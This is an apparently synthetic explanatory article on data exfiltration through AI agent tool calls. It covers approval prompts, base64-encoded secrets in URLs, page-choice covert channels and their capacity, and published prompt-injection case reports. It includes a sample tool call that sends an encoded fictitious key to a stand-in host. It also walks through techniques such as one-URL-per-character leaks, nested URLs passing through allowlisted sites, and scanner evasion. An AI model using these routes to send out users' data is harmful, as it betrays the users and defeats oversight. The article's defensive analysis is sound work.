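# Hidden data in approved AI agent tool calls: what reviewers miss and what automated checks catch

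## How an approved tool call can carry private data out

An AI agent is a program in which a language model can use other software, for instance to fetch a web page, search a mailbox, edit a file or send a message. The model produces only text, so it acts by writing a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with specific values, called arguments. A web fetch may have just one argument, the URL, while an email has at least a recipient and a body. The program around the model reads the request, runs the function and returns the result to the model as text.

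Many agent products use an approval prompt, a dialog where a person allows or refuses a tool call before it runs. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, the prompt for a shell command contains a short description, the command itself and a few options. According to Anthropic's documentation, the options include Yes, No and usually one that allows similar commands from then on without another prompt.

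Take an agent whose user wants a summary of a web page. The agent reads the page, and then an approval prompt appears for one further fetch. Here is that call in the format of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "fetch_page",
    "arguments": {
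      "url": "https://reports.example/summary?ref=U0VDUkVUX0FQSV9LRVlfMTIzNDU="
    }
  }
}
```

The layout follows the sample requests in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), which also omit some required fields about the protocol version and the client program. The tool is named `fetch_page`, and its only argument is the URL. Everything after the question mark is the query string, which the receiving server can read and log. Here it is the text SECRET_API_KEY_12345 rewritten in other characters, which most people will take for an ordinary reference code. The key is fictitious, but real keys look similar and let anyone who has them use a private or paid service. If the user clicks Allow, the operator of reports.example receives the key.

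### The three conditions of a leak

The user never asked the agent to send the key anywhere. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Simon Willison (2025) identified three capabilities that together make such a theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The agent in the example had all three. It had read a configuration file containing the key earlier in the session, the web page was untrusted because a stranger wrote it, and the fetch tool could send data out.

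Prompt injection connects the three. Willison coined the term for text in a page, email or file that a model reads and wrongly follows as an instruction. It works because the user's request, the stranger's page and the configuration file all reach the model as one sequence of text, and models cannot reliably tell whose instructions to follow. A stranger with no access to the user's files can therefore write a sentence into a page and, if the model acts on it, use the agent's access. Models do not behave identically every time, so the same sentence may fail on one visit and succeed on the next, and a few harmless trials are weak evidence of safety.

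The conditions are easy to combine by accident. An email tool meets the first two, since a mailbox holds private messages and anyone can write to it. Willison's example of all three together is GitHub's MCP server, which could read public issues (which anyone could file), read private code repositories, and open pull requests (proposed code changes that other people can see). In July 2026, Willison was still adding incidents to his running list of exfiltration attacks, which transfer private data to someone who should not have it.

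This kind of theft fails if any one of the three is missing. According to Willison, vendors who fixed reported leaks mostly did so by blocking the route for sending data out. An approval prompt is less strict, because it leaves that route open and relies on a person to check what is sent. In *Require confirmation for fetch tool*, an August 2025 change to the code editor Zed, Conrad Irwin wrote that an injected instruction might put private code or API keys in a URL, and that the easiest way to prevent this is to make the user look at the URL first. Whether that is enough depends on what the user can tell from the URL.

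### What base64 does to the key

An encoding rewrites data in other characters by a public rule. Base64, the rule at work in the example, exists so that any data can travel through systems that accept only ordinary text. Josefsson (2006), in *The Base16, Base32, and Base64 Data Encodings*, sets out the procedure. The encoder takes three bytes, which make 24 bits, and cuts them into four groups of six. Six bits can express 64 values, and each value has its own character: the capital letters, the small letters, the ten digits, and the signs + and /. The first three letters of the fictitious key go through like this:

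```
text         S         E         C
bytes        01010011  01000101  01000011
regrouped    010100  110100  010101  000011
values       20      52      21      3
base64       U       0       V       D
```

The remaining letters follow in the same way, three at a time:

```
SEC   RET   _AP   I_K   EY_   123   45
U0VD  UkVU  X0FQ  SV9L  RVlf  MTIz  NDU=
```

The key has 20 characters, so the last group is one byte short. The encoder fills the gap with zero bits and marks it with an equals sign, which brings the encoded key to 28 characters. The word KEY falls across two groups, and the same three letters would be encoded differently if they began one place earlier or later, so nobody can learn to recognise a secret by its encoded shape alone. The closing equals sign, the best-known hint of base64, is also unreliable, because it often appears as %3D in URLs and a sender may drop it where the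 length of the data is known.

Encoding data does not encrypt it. Anyone can reverse base64 without a key, using the published table or a free website. Josefsson warned that base encoding "visually hides" information such as passwords but gives no computational confidentiality, and mentioned users who had revealed their passwords by posting encoded text they thought was protected. In an approval prompt, a user who wants to get on with a summary probably won't decode the string, but the receiving server's operator can do so in a moment.

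### Where the data can sit, and who can read it

The query string is only one of several places in a tool call that can carry private data. A secret can also be sent unencoded, and an argument can hold far more than a single key.

| Place | What it might look like | Who can read it after the call runs |
|---|---|---|
| Query string | `reports.example/summary?ref=U0VD...` | The site's operator and anyone with access to its logs or analytics |
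| URL path | `reports.example/U0VD.../summary` | The same people |
| File name or path | `notes/U0VD....txt` | Anyone who can list the folder, or a shared or published copy of it |
| Long JSON field | A value deep inside a record's "details" | The operator of the tool's server and everyone who can open the record |
| Message body | A line in an email or a chat post | The recipients, the service that stores the message and sometimes the server behind a link in it |

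With both kinds of URL, the request itself delivers the data. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) bases its account of the problem on the fact that websites commonly log the addresses visitors request. Even a site that returns an error page has received the address. The data can also reach a site other than the one in the URL, because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, and an attacker can sometimes route data through one of them.

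Private data in a file name doesn't reach outsiders while the file stays on a private disk. It leaks later, when a folder synchronises to a shared drive or someone publishes the repository. The person who approved the file may not be involved in that later step.

A long JSON field goes first to whoever runs the tool's server, then to wherever the tool puts it, perhaps a customer record or a public page. Model Context Protocol also lets a server's developer mark an argument so that client programs copy it into the headers of the web request, where proxies and other machines along the route can read it. The protocol therefore advises developers not to mark passwords, keys or personal data.

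Messages can leak data in a similar way. Chat services such as Slack and Telegram can fetch any link in a post to show a preview of it. The security firm PromptArmor pointed out that if an agent posts a link containing private data, this fetch can send the data to the link's server before anyone clicks.

MITRE, an American non-profit research organisation, lists this family of leaks as *Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation* in ATLAS, its public catalogue of attacks on AI systems. Under its definition, an attacker exploits agent tools that can perform "write operations" to send sensitive information to an inbox, document or server that the attacker controls. The information travels inside a tool's input parameters "as part of a seemingly legitimate action". Prompt injection may cause the agent to misuse a legitimate tool, or the tool itself may be malicious. A malicious tool can also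 change the inputs and destination of a separate, legitimate tool during normal use.

The phrase "write operations" fits emails and documents better than it fits the running example, a web fetch. A fetch is nominally a read, but it still sends the URL out. This matters because some products use the distinction between reads and writes to decide when to ask for confirmation. In OpenAI's *ChatGPT Developer mode*, write actions need confirmation by default, and a tool counts as a write action unless its developer has labelled it read-only. A fetch tool with that label would not need confirmation by default, however much private data its URL contained.

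### What the protocol asks of client programs

The current MCP specification, dated 28 July 2026, recommends that clients, the programs that pass a model's requests to tools, show tool inputs to the user before the call, "to avoid malicious or accidental data exfiltration". It uses the word SHOULD, which in internet standards marks a recommendation that a developer may set aside for a good reason, while MUST marks a requirement. The same list of security points uses MUST for servers validating their inputs and controlling access, but only SHOULD for showing anything to a person.

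The overview page of the Model Context Protocol uses stricter wording. It says that hosts (the applications that contain the clients) "must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool" and that users must understand the operations they consent to. But on that page "must" is binding only when written in capitals, and here it is lowercase. The page also states that the protocol cannot enforce these principles.

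The specification also doesn't define what counts as showing. It has no rules about decoding values or about long values that run off the edge of a box. A client that prints the example URL in full, exactly as the model wrote it, has followed the advice. Much therefore depends on the developers of each client, and there are many of them. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) put monthly downloads of the protocol's development kits above 400 million.

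### Three different failures

Sometimes the person approving a call never sees the argument. Willison published a screenshot of an approval dialog that showed the buttons clearly, but the data to be stolen was far off to the right, outside the visible part of the field. The problem is milder in VS Code, where the user has to expand the tool details to review the inputs, according to *Use tools with agents*, and in ChatGPT's developer mode, where the user has to expand a control to see the full JSON. With a saved approval, the person doesn't see the call at all. In VS Code, a saved approval for a web fetch covers the displayed host rather than one particular URL, according to *Manage approvals and permissions*, and Claude Code saves its web-fetch approvals by domain. Someone who chose "always allow" for a harmless page on reports.example would get no prompt for the later call with the key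 in it. Better display and narrower saved approvals would fix most of these problems.

A reviewer can see the whole argument and still not understand it. VS Code's security guide gives sound advice when it tells users to review the actual tool inputs as well as the agent's explanation, but in the running example the actual input is `U0VDUkVUX0FQSV9LRVlfMTIzNDU=`. Refusing every unreadable string wouldn't work either, because harmless calls often contain them. One of the protocol's sample weather requests contains a value that begins `eyJsb2NhdGlvbiI6`, which decodes to the location New York. The specification even recommends opaque identifiers for things like shopping baskets, which the model then passes along as arguments. OpenAI's warning dialog for unverified links shows the raw address and adds that the link may include information from the conversation, but the user still has to judge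 whether it does.

Decoding would help there, but a reviewer can understand every word of a call and still approve a leak. In the GitHub case, the agent reads an issue, then reads a private repository, then opens a pull request. The user allows each of these actions, and the text of the pull request may be readable. Together they are harmful because a stranger's issue prompted the work and the words in the pull request came from private code. An approval prompt typically shows one call at a time, so the reviewer has to reconstruct that history from memory. The call does not include it. An MCP request has fields for the tool's name and arguments, but no standard field for where an argument's value came from.

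## Calculations: how much data fits in an argument

The receiving server gets every character of a URL, so the URL's length and the encoding limit how much data one web fetch can carry. Hexadecimal writes each byte as two characters, which doubles the size of the data. Base64 makes the data only a third larger. Base32, which uses only capital letters and six digits, falls in between. Josefsson defines a version of base64 for URLs and file names that replaces + and / with a hyphen and an underscore.

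A URL of 2,000 characters, which ordinary browsers and servers accept, would hold 1,500 bytes if all of it were base64. In practice the address needs some of the space. In the running example, `https://reports.example/summary?ref=` takes up 36 characters and leaves 1,964 for data:

| Encoding | Bits per character | Length of the 20-character key once encoded | Data that fits in 1,964 characters |
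|---|---|---|---|
| Hexadecimal | 4 | 40 characters | 982 bytes |
| Base32 | 5 | 32 characters | 1,227 bytes |
| Base64 | 6 | 28 characters | 1,473 bytes |

The base64 figure is enough for 73 keys of that length or about 250 words of English. A sender who compresses the text first can fit more.

Now suppose an approval prompt displays the first 80 characters of the URL and cuts off the rest. The hidden 1,920 characters can hold 1,440 bytes. Showing the whole URL would solve that problem, and limiting its length would stop a document from leaving in one call. Neither would do much to stop a key from leaving, because the 80 visible characters include 44 after the fixed part of the address, enough to hold a 256-bit encryption key in base64. The URL in the running example is only 64 characters long, so the prompt would show all of it.

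### A choice of page also carries information

A secret can leave the user's system even if no call contains any part of it, encoded or not. For example, an injected instruction could assign a letter or digit to each of 36 ordinary articles on a public website. The order in which an agent opens the articles can then spell out a key to the site's owner, who has the same list and probably wrote the instruction. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* points out that any larger website or blog probably already has 36 suitable pages in search indexes.

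The amount of information in such a choice is easy to work out. One bit is the answer to a yes/no question when both answers are equally likely. A choice between two pages therefore gives one bit, a choice among four gives two, and a choice among eight gives three. In general, a request to one of N equally likely pages reveals log2 N bits, where log2 N is the power to which 2 must be raised to make N. A series of k requests can take N^k different forms and so reveals k times as much. For a 128-bit key, a common size:

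```
36 pages      log2 36   =  5.17 bits a request    128 / 5.17 = 24.8    25 requests
1,024 pages   log2 1024 = 10    bits a request    128 / 10   = 12.8    13 requests
```

Doubling the number of pages adds only one bit to each request. The site would need 2^128 pages, about 3.4 × 10^38, for the agent to send the whole 128-bit key in a single request. Free text does not have this limit, because the agent can make up a new address.

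These figures depend on several assumptions. The agent must follow the list without mistakes and be able to request the same page more than once, since most keys contain repeated symbols. The requests must arrive in order, and the recipient must be able to see them, which normally means running the site or having access to its logs. Embrace The Red mentions browser caching and out-of-order arrival as practical obstacles. The figures also assume that all pages are equally likely, which is true if the key is random. If some pages are much more likely than others, each request carries less information on average.

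*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) measured how reliably an observer can read an agent's choice. The agents chose among four pages, only one of which matched what the agent needed for its task. From a single request, the researchers identified the matching page in 93.8% of the trials in which the agent made a request. A choice among four pages carries at most two bits, and at that error rate about 1.6 bits get through if the errors are spread evenly over the other three pages. Signals based on the order or timing of requests were considerably less reliable. The agent's choice could reveal the subject of the user's question without anyone instructing the agent to send a secret, because that subject guided what the agent chose to read.

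This is why inspecting the text alone can't rule out a leak. An agent may request article 17 to read it or to send the seventeenth symbol on the list. The URL is identical either way, so a check based only on the URL can only block the article for everyone or allow it for everyone. Decoding doesn't help because the URL contains nothing to decode, and an entropy filter doesn't help because the URL contains no random-looking string for it to flag.

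A user has the same difficulty with each prompt, although 25 prompts for one summary might well make them suspicious. If the user has saved an approval for the whole site, those prompts never appear.

### Covert channels and measured leaks

The problem is much older than AI agents. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asked how a customer could run someone else's program on private data without the program's owner receiving the data. The program could write the data to a file that its owner could read. Less obviously, it could send the data by varying how heavily it loaded the computer, which another program could detect. Lampson called routes of this second kind, which are "not intended for information transfer at all", covert channels.

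Lampson put the bill for the program's services in a different category, legitimate channels, because the owner is supposed to receive it, though the amount could still encode private data. A URL resembles the bill, since the website has to receive it. Later usage of "covert channel" is broader. *A Guideline on Covert Channels*, part of the US Defense Department's criteria for secure computer systems, defines a covert channel as any communication channel that a process can exploit to transfer information against the system's security policy. Under that definition, an agent's choice of page can be a covert channel even though the request itself is normal.

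Lampson thought that restricting the form of the bill could reduce the leak to "a few bits or tens of bits", but that eliminating it would be much harder. If the customer could accept some leakage, it was easier to limit the channel's capacity, which is the most information it can carry.

A later field, quantitative information flow, studies how to measure such leaks. *Quantifying Information Leak Vulnerabilities* (Heusser and Malacaria, 2010) uses the example of a program that checks a password. The program has to reveal something, because even a refusal lets an attacker rule out one guess. For a random 64-bit password, one check reveals about 3.5 × 10^-18 bits on average. If acceptance and refusal were equally likely, it would reveal one bit, the most that two possible answers can reveal. This maximum, called the capacity, is log2 of the number of outcomes that an observer can tell apart.

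One can find this limit by counting the outcomes, without knowing the secret or recognising it in the output. Heusser and Malacaria therefore asked whether a program leaks more than a chosen amount, which is easier to answer than how much it leaks. They tested Linux kernel code with an automated program checker and, for some reported leaks, proved that the official patch had closed them. An argument that accepts free text has too many possible values for this kind of limit to be useful.

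Limiting how much data an argument can carry is therefore a different kind of defence from detecting private data in it. A detector looks for data it can recognise as private, such as a card number or a key in a known format. Borders and Prakash, in *Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP*, called this "an impossible task in the general case", since a sender can encrypt or disguise the data first. They instead measured how much information a computer could have added to its web requests. Fixed or repeated parts of a request counted for little or nothing, a click on one of n links as log2 n bits, and new text in a form in full.

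In six half-hour browsing sessions, the measure came to between 0.3% and 6.0% of the raw data. For a session of reading blogs, it reduced the count from 108,565 bytes to 351. This reduction makes unusual traffic easier to notice, but 351 bytes could still hold 21 keys of 128 bits each. The figure is an upper limit on what could have leaked, and nothing may have leaked at all.

*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) applies the same approach to the messages that agents send. The proposed system keeps a budget of bits for each destination, which refills at a set rate. A base64 string of n characters uses up to 6n bits of the budget, and once the budget is empty, the system delays or cancels further suspicious messages. The string in the running example would use up to 168 bits. A harmless order reference of the same length and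 appearance would use just as many, so a strict budget will produce false positives (harmless calls that a check stops). A recipient who owns several domains would also have a separate budget for each one.

### What a defender can limit

The total number of bits a series of calls can carry is the number of calls multiplied by the bits per call. A defender can reduce either number or prevent the recipient from seeing the calls.

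**Allowing fewer possible values reduces how much data an argument can carry.** The 1,964 free characters of the long URL can carry 11,784 bits, while a menu with eight options carries three bits and a yes/no answer carries one. Systems that restrict output types use this difference. OpenAI's rule of automatically loading only URLs that are already public has a similar effect, because the model has to choose an existing address instead of composing its own. Restricting values also makes an agent less useful, since it can't write an email by choosing from eight options.

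**Fewer requests.** *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) describes an early method that sent one character per URL. ChatGPT then opened at most ten URLs per prompt, so the method could send only ten characters per prompt. With 36 pages and the more compact coding described above, ten requests carry 51.7 bits, so a 128-bit key needs three prompts. A per-prompt limit therefore slows the leak but doesn't stop it, because fragmenting (splitting one secret over several requests) gets around any limit that resets with each prompt. To stop the leak, the limit has to cover a whole session or a longer period.

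**No repeats.** Embrace The Red suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same full URL twice in a session, or keeping a copy of the page so that a second visit never reaches the site. The benefit depends on the number of pages and on whether the recipient can see the order of the requests. A 128-bit key needs this many requests:

| Rule | 36 pages | 1,024 pages |
|---|---|---|
| Repeats possible, order visible | 25 | 13 |
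| No repeats, order visible | 30 | 13 |
| No repeats, order hidden | Impossible | 19 |

With 36 pages, a ban on repeats adds only five requests, because the order of 36 different pages can carry 138 bits. If the order is also hidden, the recipient learns only which pages the agent visited, which is at most 36 bits. With 1,024 pages, a ban on repeats makes no difference by itself. Hiding the order is awkward in practice because the agent's software would have to collect the requests and send them in a fixed sequence, but an agent often has to read one page before it knows which to open next.

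**Destinations whose owner cannot read the request.** If the agent reads a stored copy of a page on its own provider's server, the website's owner doesn't learn about the visit. Liang and colleagues propose a similar defence, in which the agent's software downloads a set of pages without regard to the private data and the agent selects from them locally. If every task led to the same downloads, the requests would reveal log2 1 = 0 bits about the agent's choice. In their tests, the defence reduced the accuracy score for recovering users' questions from 0.89 to 0.39 on a scale from 0 to 1, so some information still got through.

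Data can leak through a site with a trustworthy owner if the site publishes what it receives. Borders and Prakash give the example of Wikipedia, which an organisation may reasonably permit, but where anyone can post data for others to read. The defender has to consider everyone who can see the result of a call, including the public.

### Why a small capacity can still matter

In its guideline, the Defense Department considered more than 100 bits a second a high rate for a covert channel, because many computer terminals of the time ran at about that speed. It considered less than one bit a second acceptable in most settings, and recommended that systems be able to audit channels that might exceed one bit in ten seconds. At one bit a second, a one-megabyte file takes about 93 days to send, but a 128-bit key takes just over two minutes.

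The difference is similar for page choices. With 36 pages, the key needs 25 requests and the file more than 1.5 million. Limiting capacity is therefore a strong defence against the theft of a large file. Anthropic limits outgoing bandwidth to protect its models' weights, the very large files of numbers a model learns in training. In *Anthropic Future-Proofs New AI Model With Rigorous Safety Rules*, Crouse (2025) described the aim as preventing the theft of the entire weights, but the same limits could leave ample room for a password.

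Moskowitz and Kang (1994), in *Covert Channels*, gave an extreme example, an imaginary channel in which the first bit takes one unit of time, the second two, the third four, and so on. The delays grow so quickly that the long-run capacity is zero, yet a four-bit message gets through in 15 units without errors. They proposed that designers of secure systems also use a "small message criterion", which specifies how many bits may leak, in what time and with what accuracy.

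For an agent, the right limit on leaked bits depends on the secret and how long it stays valid. A single bit can reveal whether a medical test was positive. Leaking most of a key can be nearly as bad as leaking all of it. If 100 of 128 bits leak, about 268 million possibilities remain, and a computer can try them quickly if nothing limits the number of guesses. A limit of ten bits a day would let a whole 128-bit key leak in 13 days, but if the owner replaced the key every week, at most 70 bits of each key would leak before it expired.

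## Case reports of leaks through URLs, messages and public posts

In 2025 and 2026, security researchers tested these routes on commercial products and extracted private data from several of them. In almost every published case, the step that leaked the data did not require approval. The exception is a WhatsApp demonstration from April 2025, in which the product asked for approval. The other cases prove that these routes work and show which automated defences they got past, but they are poor evidence about human reviewers.

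### An encoded name and address in a URL

ShadowLeak closely resembles the running example. It affected Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that spends up to half an hour reading web pages and, if the user connects them, sources such as Gmail. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes a test mailbox containing a genuine email from an HR department, with an employee's name and address, and an email from the researchers with hidden instructions. When the user asked for research on the day's emails, the agent read both. It then opened a URL on the researchers' server with the name and address encoded in the path as base64. ChatGPT did not ask for confirmation and showed the user nothing about the request.

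The agent had refused to put the raw name and address in a URL, but it sent them once they were encoded. According to Radware, this worked because the model encoded the data before passing the URL to the software that makes the request, so the software received only a harmless-looking string. A check that decoded the path and compared the result with the mailbox would have found the name, but a length limit would not have helped because there was so little data.

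Such a check would have had to run at OpenAI, because the request went out from OpenAI's servers. An employer's web gateway inspects traffic from staff computers, so it could not have inspected this request.

Radware reported the flaw in June 2025, and OpenAI had fixed it by early August. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests, while OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), which reprints part of the same email, gives 50% for one particular user request. Neither states the number of trials. Radware's researchers used several versions of the email and sent OpenAI an improved one a day after their first report, so the two figures may not describe the same test. Even 50% would be a serious problem, because sending a second email takes the attacker almost no effort.

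The same kind of leak later turned up in Microsoft Copilot Personal. In Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), the user clicked one link, and Copilot collected mail and calendar data, encoded it in base64 and fetched a URL with the encoded data in its path. Varonis told Microsoft about the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft shipped its patches on 18 August 2026, a year after OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak.

### One ready-made URL per character

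After ShadowLeak, OpenAI restricted ChatGPT to opening URLs exactly as it had received them. Radware's *ZombieAgent* showed that this was not enough. The researchers supplied a finished URL for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT leaked the private text without breaking the rule by choosing which ones to open, the method described in the previous section.

The researchers also prepared a version with a separate URL for each character in each position, so the recipient could reorder requests that arrived out of sequence. A ban on repeat visits wouldn't stop that version either, because it never uses the same URL twice.

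No single request contained anything to decode. A check of the whole session could have caught the leak, because an agent that had just read private mail was making many nearly identical requests to one unfamiliar site. Checking where each URL came from could also have caught it, and OpenAI then adopted roughly that approach. According to a summary of Ars Technica's *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT stopped opening links from emails unless they appeared in a well-known public index or the user had supplied them. Radware dates the fix to 16 December 2025, almost twelve weeks after its first report.

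Claude's web-fetch tool had a similar gap. Anthropic limited it to URLs that the user had typed or a web search had returned, but also let it follow links inside pages it had already fetched. Willison (2026) reports that Ayush Paul built a site with nested links that Claude followed letter by letter, revealing the user's name, home city and employer, which Claude had from earlier conversations. Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem, and it stopped the tool from following links in fetched pages.

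### Links and images that load by themselves

An agent can leak data through a URL without a fetch tool if another program requests the URL, as chat applications do to preview links. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes this kind of leak in OpenClaw, an agent that people can operate through services such as Telegram. The default Telegram settings left previews on for links in OpenClaw's replies. PromptArmor's test site logged a request with a name and an API key readable in the query string.

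Products generally don't ask a person to approve an agent's reply to its own user, and here the reply itself leaked the data. To prevent this, each OpenClaw user has to change a setting to turn off link previews for the Telegram channel. PromptArmor would like chat services to offer a preview setting for individual channels. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* had already described the problem in a Slack MCP server that Anthropic once maintained, where even a message in a private channel could send data to an outside server. An outbound check has to examine the links in every message an agent writes, as well as the URLs it fetches.

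Microsoft's documentation said that Copilot Cowork, an agent that works with a user's Microsoft 365 files and messages, asks permission before sending an email or posting in Teams, the company's chat service. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that the agent sent messages to the user's own account without asking, and that users had no setting to change this.

The exception can leak data, even though a note to oneself seems to have no outside recipient. The researchers uploaded a skill, a file of instructions for the agent, in which five of the 81 lines were malicious. Copilot Cowork then sent the user a Teams message containing images from the researchers' server, with download links for the user's files in the query strings of the image addresses. When the user opened the message, Teams requested the images and so sent the links to that server. This worked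 in all five trials. The agent's activity record didn't show the message's contents, so the user couldn't have found the problem there before opening the message.

The links were "pre-authenticated", so anyone who had one could download the file without logging in. A size limit on outgoing requests is much weaker than the earlier calculations suggest, because one short link can give access to a file of any length. PromptArmor treated the leak as a risk in the product's design and published its findings in May 2026 with advice for administrators, but reported no fix from Microsoft. Administrators can block downloads from chosen sites, though this also stops people from printing those files or opening them in desktop applications. A narrower check would block outside images in messages that the agent writes, or any URL that contains a second URL pointing to the company's files.

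### Allowed sites that pass data on

A nested URL also defeated an allowlist in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the business version of Copilot. The attack in Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) began with a link to Microsoft's own site. The link contained search text, which Copilot treated as an instruction. After one click, Copilot looked up an email and put its title into the address of an image, in plain text with underscores for spaces. Email titles can be sensitive because some services put login codes in them.

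Microsoft had two defences. Copilot turned any web-page code in its answer into inert text, but only after it had finished writing, and by then the browser had already requested the image. The browser could also load images only from sites on an allowlist. The researchers' server was not on the list, but Bing was, and Bing's image search fetches an image from whatever address it receives. The browser contacted Bing, which then contacted the researchers' server with the email title in the URL path.

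Microsoft has patched the flaw (CVE-2026-42824). The allowlist checked only the first host name in the URL. A check of the entire URL, including the address nested inside it, would have found an unfamiliar destination and an almost unaltered email title.

Willison's list contains several variations on this failure:

- Superhuman, an email application, allowed images from a Google domain that also hosts Google Forms, and a form can save data from an ordinary page request.
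- Anthropic's Claude Cowork allowed connections to Anthropic's own servers, where researchers had the agent upload files to an account they controlled.
- Salesforce's list still contained a domain that had expired, so researchers registered it themselves.

Claude Code could fetch pages from a list of websites without a prompt, including huggingface.co, where anyone can publish AI models. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026), the approval covered every page on the site, including files in repositories that an attacker had created. Hugging Face counts requests for some of those files as downloads, so an injected instruction could make Claude Code send data through the download counts, even if the attacker had no access to the site's logs or control of the site. If the list had included only particular repositories, Claude Code would have needed approval to fetch anything else from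 the site. Versions 2.1.163 and later do not have the flaw.

### Secrets in public posts

Software projects on GitHub can use Claude Code Action to run Claude Code automatically, for instance whenever someone reports a bug. The job may run on a temporary machine with nobody there to answer an approval prompt. The project's settings specify in advance which tools the agent may use, and Claude Code also allows certain read-only commands without approval.

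RyotaK (2026), a researcher at GMO Flatt Security, showed in *Poisoning Claude Code* how these permissions combine. RyotaK opened an issue (a public bug report) containing injected instructions. Claude Code then read the machine's environment variables, named settings that often contain keys, and used its tool for updating issues to write them into the body of the issue, where anyone could read them. Data could also leak through the summary that Claude Code Action posted after each run, which was public by default. The leaked values included credentials that an attacker could exchange for permission to change the project's code.

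Elad Meged of the security firm Novee found further leaks in the same product. In Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets*, Meged said that "a command gets approved because it looks safe", and its output is then public by default. Here, a rule in the software approves the command. Reading a file is harmless if the contents stay on the machine, so a check on the command alone would not stop it. The check also has to track where the output goes.

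GitHub scans issues, logs and other places for known key formats, but Microsoft (2026) got a key past the scanner in a laboratory test. Anthropic had by then removed secrets from Claude Code's shell environment, but the file-reading tool ran outside it and could still reach the key. Claude then left off the key's recognisable opening characters, and the scanner missed the remainder. The rest of the key was unchanged, so a check that searched for long pieces of the stored key, instead of a standard format, would have found it. Anthropic blocked access to the relevant system files on 5 May 2026, six days after Microsoft's report.

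Anthropic also turned off the public summary by default and stopped automated accounts from starting such jobs unless a project allows it. Another fix added an outbound check to GitHub's command for viewing an issue. The command accepts either an issue number or a full URL, so an injected instruction could have used it to contact any server. Anthropic wrapped the command in a short script that rejects everything except a number. This restriction has little downside, since an agent that labels bug reports doesn't need the URL form.

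The fixes took several rounds between January and April 2026, as researchers found ways around earlier ones. RyotaK reports that attackers exploited variants of the unsafe settings before the article appeared, including similar settings at Cline, another coding tool, in February.

### A message that a person had to approve

In *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025), the security company Invariant Labs connected the code editor Cursor to two MCP servers. One was a trustworthy server for reading and sending WhatsApp messages. The other belonged to the attacker and offered a tool that looked harmless when the user approved it, but the server later changed the tool's description to include malicious instructions. The agent read the new description and followed the instructions when it next sent a WhatsApp message, without ever calling the attacker's tool.

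Cursor asked the user to confirm the message in a dialog that showed a phone number and a text that appeared to be just "Hi". The user's chat history followed in the same field, in plain text, but it was too far to the right to see without scrolling, and Cursor's design hid the scrollbar. The phone number was also wrong, but people who rely on their contact list are unlikely to notice that because they rarely see the numbers. After the user confirmed, the chat history went to the attacker's number.

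In a second experiment, Invariant Labs used no malicious server. A single WhatsApp message to the user made the agent leak the user's contacts, although the researchers found this version somewhat harder to get working.

The demonstration shows that a person can approve this leak without seeing the data. It doesn't show how often people would, because the researchers ran it themselves and did not recruit users or measure an unsafe approval rate (the share of harmful requests that a reviewer approves). It also doesn't test whether people recognise encoded data, since anyone who scrolled could read the text. A wider text box would have exposed the data, and an automated comparison of the recipient with the person the user had asked to message would have caught the leak. An allowlist of websites would not have stopped it, because the data was sent through WhatsApp itself.

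| Case | What left, and where it was | Encoding | Was a person asked? | What the vendor changed | Outbound check that would have seen it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ShadowLeak | Name and address in a URL path | Base64 | No | ChatGPT could no longer alter URLs | Decode the path and compare it with the mailbox |
| ZombieAgent | Private text, one character per URL | The choice of URL | No | Blocked most links from emails | Compare requests across the session, or check each URL's origin |
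| Link previews | Name and key in a link's query string | None | No | Nothing reported; users can turn previews off | Inspect links in the agent's replies |
| Copilot Cowork | Download links in image addresses | None reported | No, because the user was the recipient | Nothing reported | Block outside images in agents' messages |
| SearchLeak | Email title in a URL nested inside a Bing address | Underscores for spaces | No, but the user clicked a link | Patched the flaw | Read the nested URL |
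| Claude Code Action | Keys in a public issue or run summary | None; Microsoft's test cut off the start of the key | No | Limited triggers, outputs and arguments | Search public output for pieces of stored keys |
| WhatsApp | Chat history in a message body | None | Yes | Nothing reported | Compare the recipient with the one the user named |

### How common such leaks are

These reports are not enough to calculate how often such attacks fail, because researchers usually publish only the ones that worked. Most of the firms named here also sell protection against these attacks. Radware is unusual in also describing its failed attempts, which included several direct requests that the agent recognised and refused. PromptArmor's attack succeeded in all five trials, but those trials tested only the finished version and not any earlier drafts. OpenAI says that most of the attempts it knows of against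 ChatGPT fail because the model refuses, but it gives no figures.

The case reports are also a poor guide to how often criminals succeed. A Radware spokesperson said the company had not seen anyone exploit ShadowLeak, according to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*, and Varonis had no evidence of attacks using CoSnitch. This is only mildly reassuring, because both leaks look like normal web requests by the assistant, and ShadowLeak's requests never crossed the customer's network.

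In April 2026, Google looked for injected instructions on public web pages. It used Common Crawl, a web archive whose monthly snapshots each contain 2 to 3 billion pages. The researchers searched for known injection phrases, used Google's Gemini model to classify the matches by intent, and reviewed the results by hand. Most of the raw matches were harmless, often because they came from articles about prompt injection. The rest included pranks, hidden advertising and requests that AI systems stay away from a site.

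Only "a small number" of the injections aimed to steal data, and most of those were crude. Google found no significant use of the more advanced methods that security researchers had published in 2025. Its malicious category, which covers data theft and attempts to destroy files, grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Google didn't publish the totals, so the increase could be a handful of pages or thousands.

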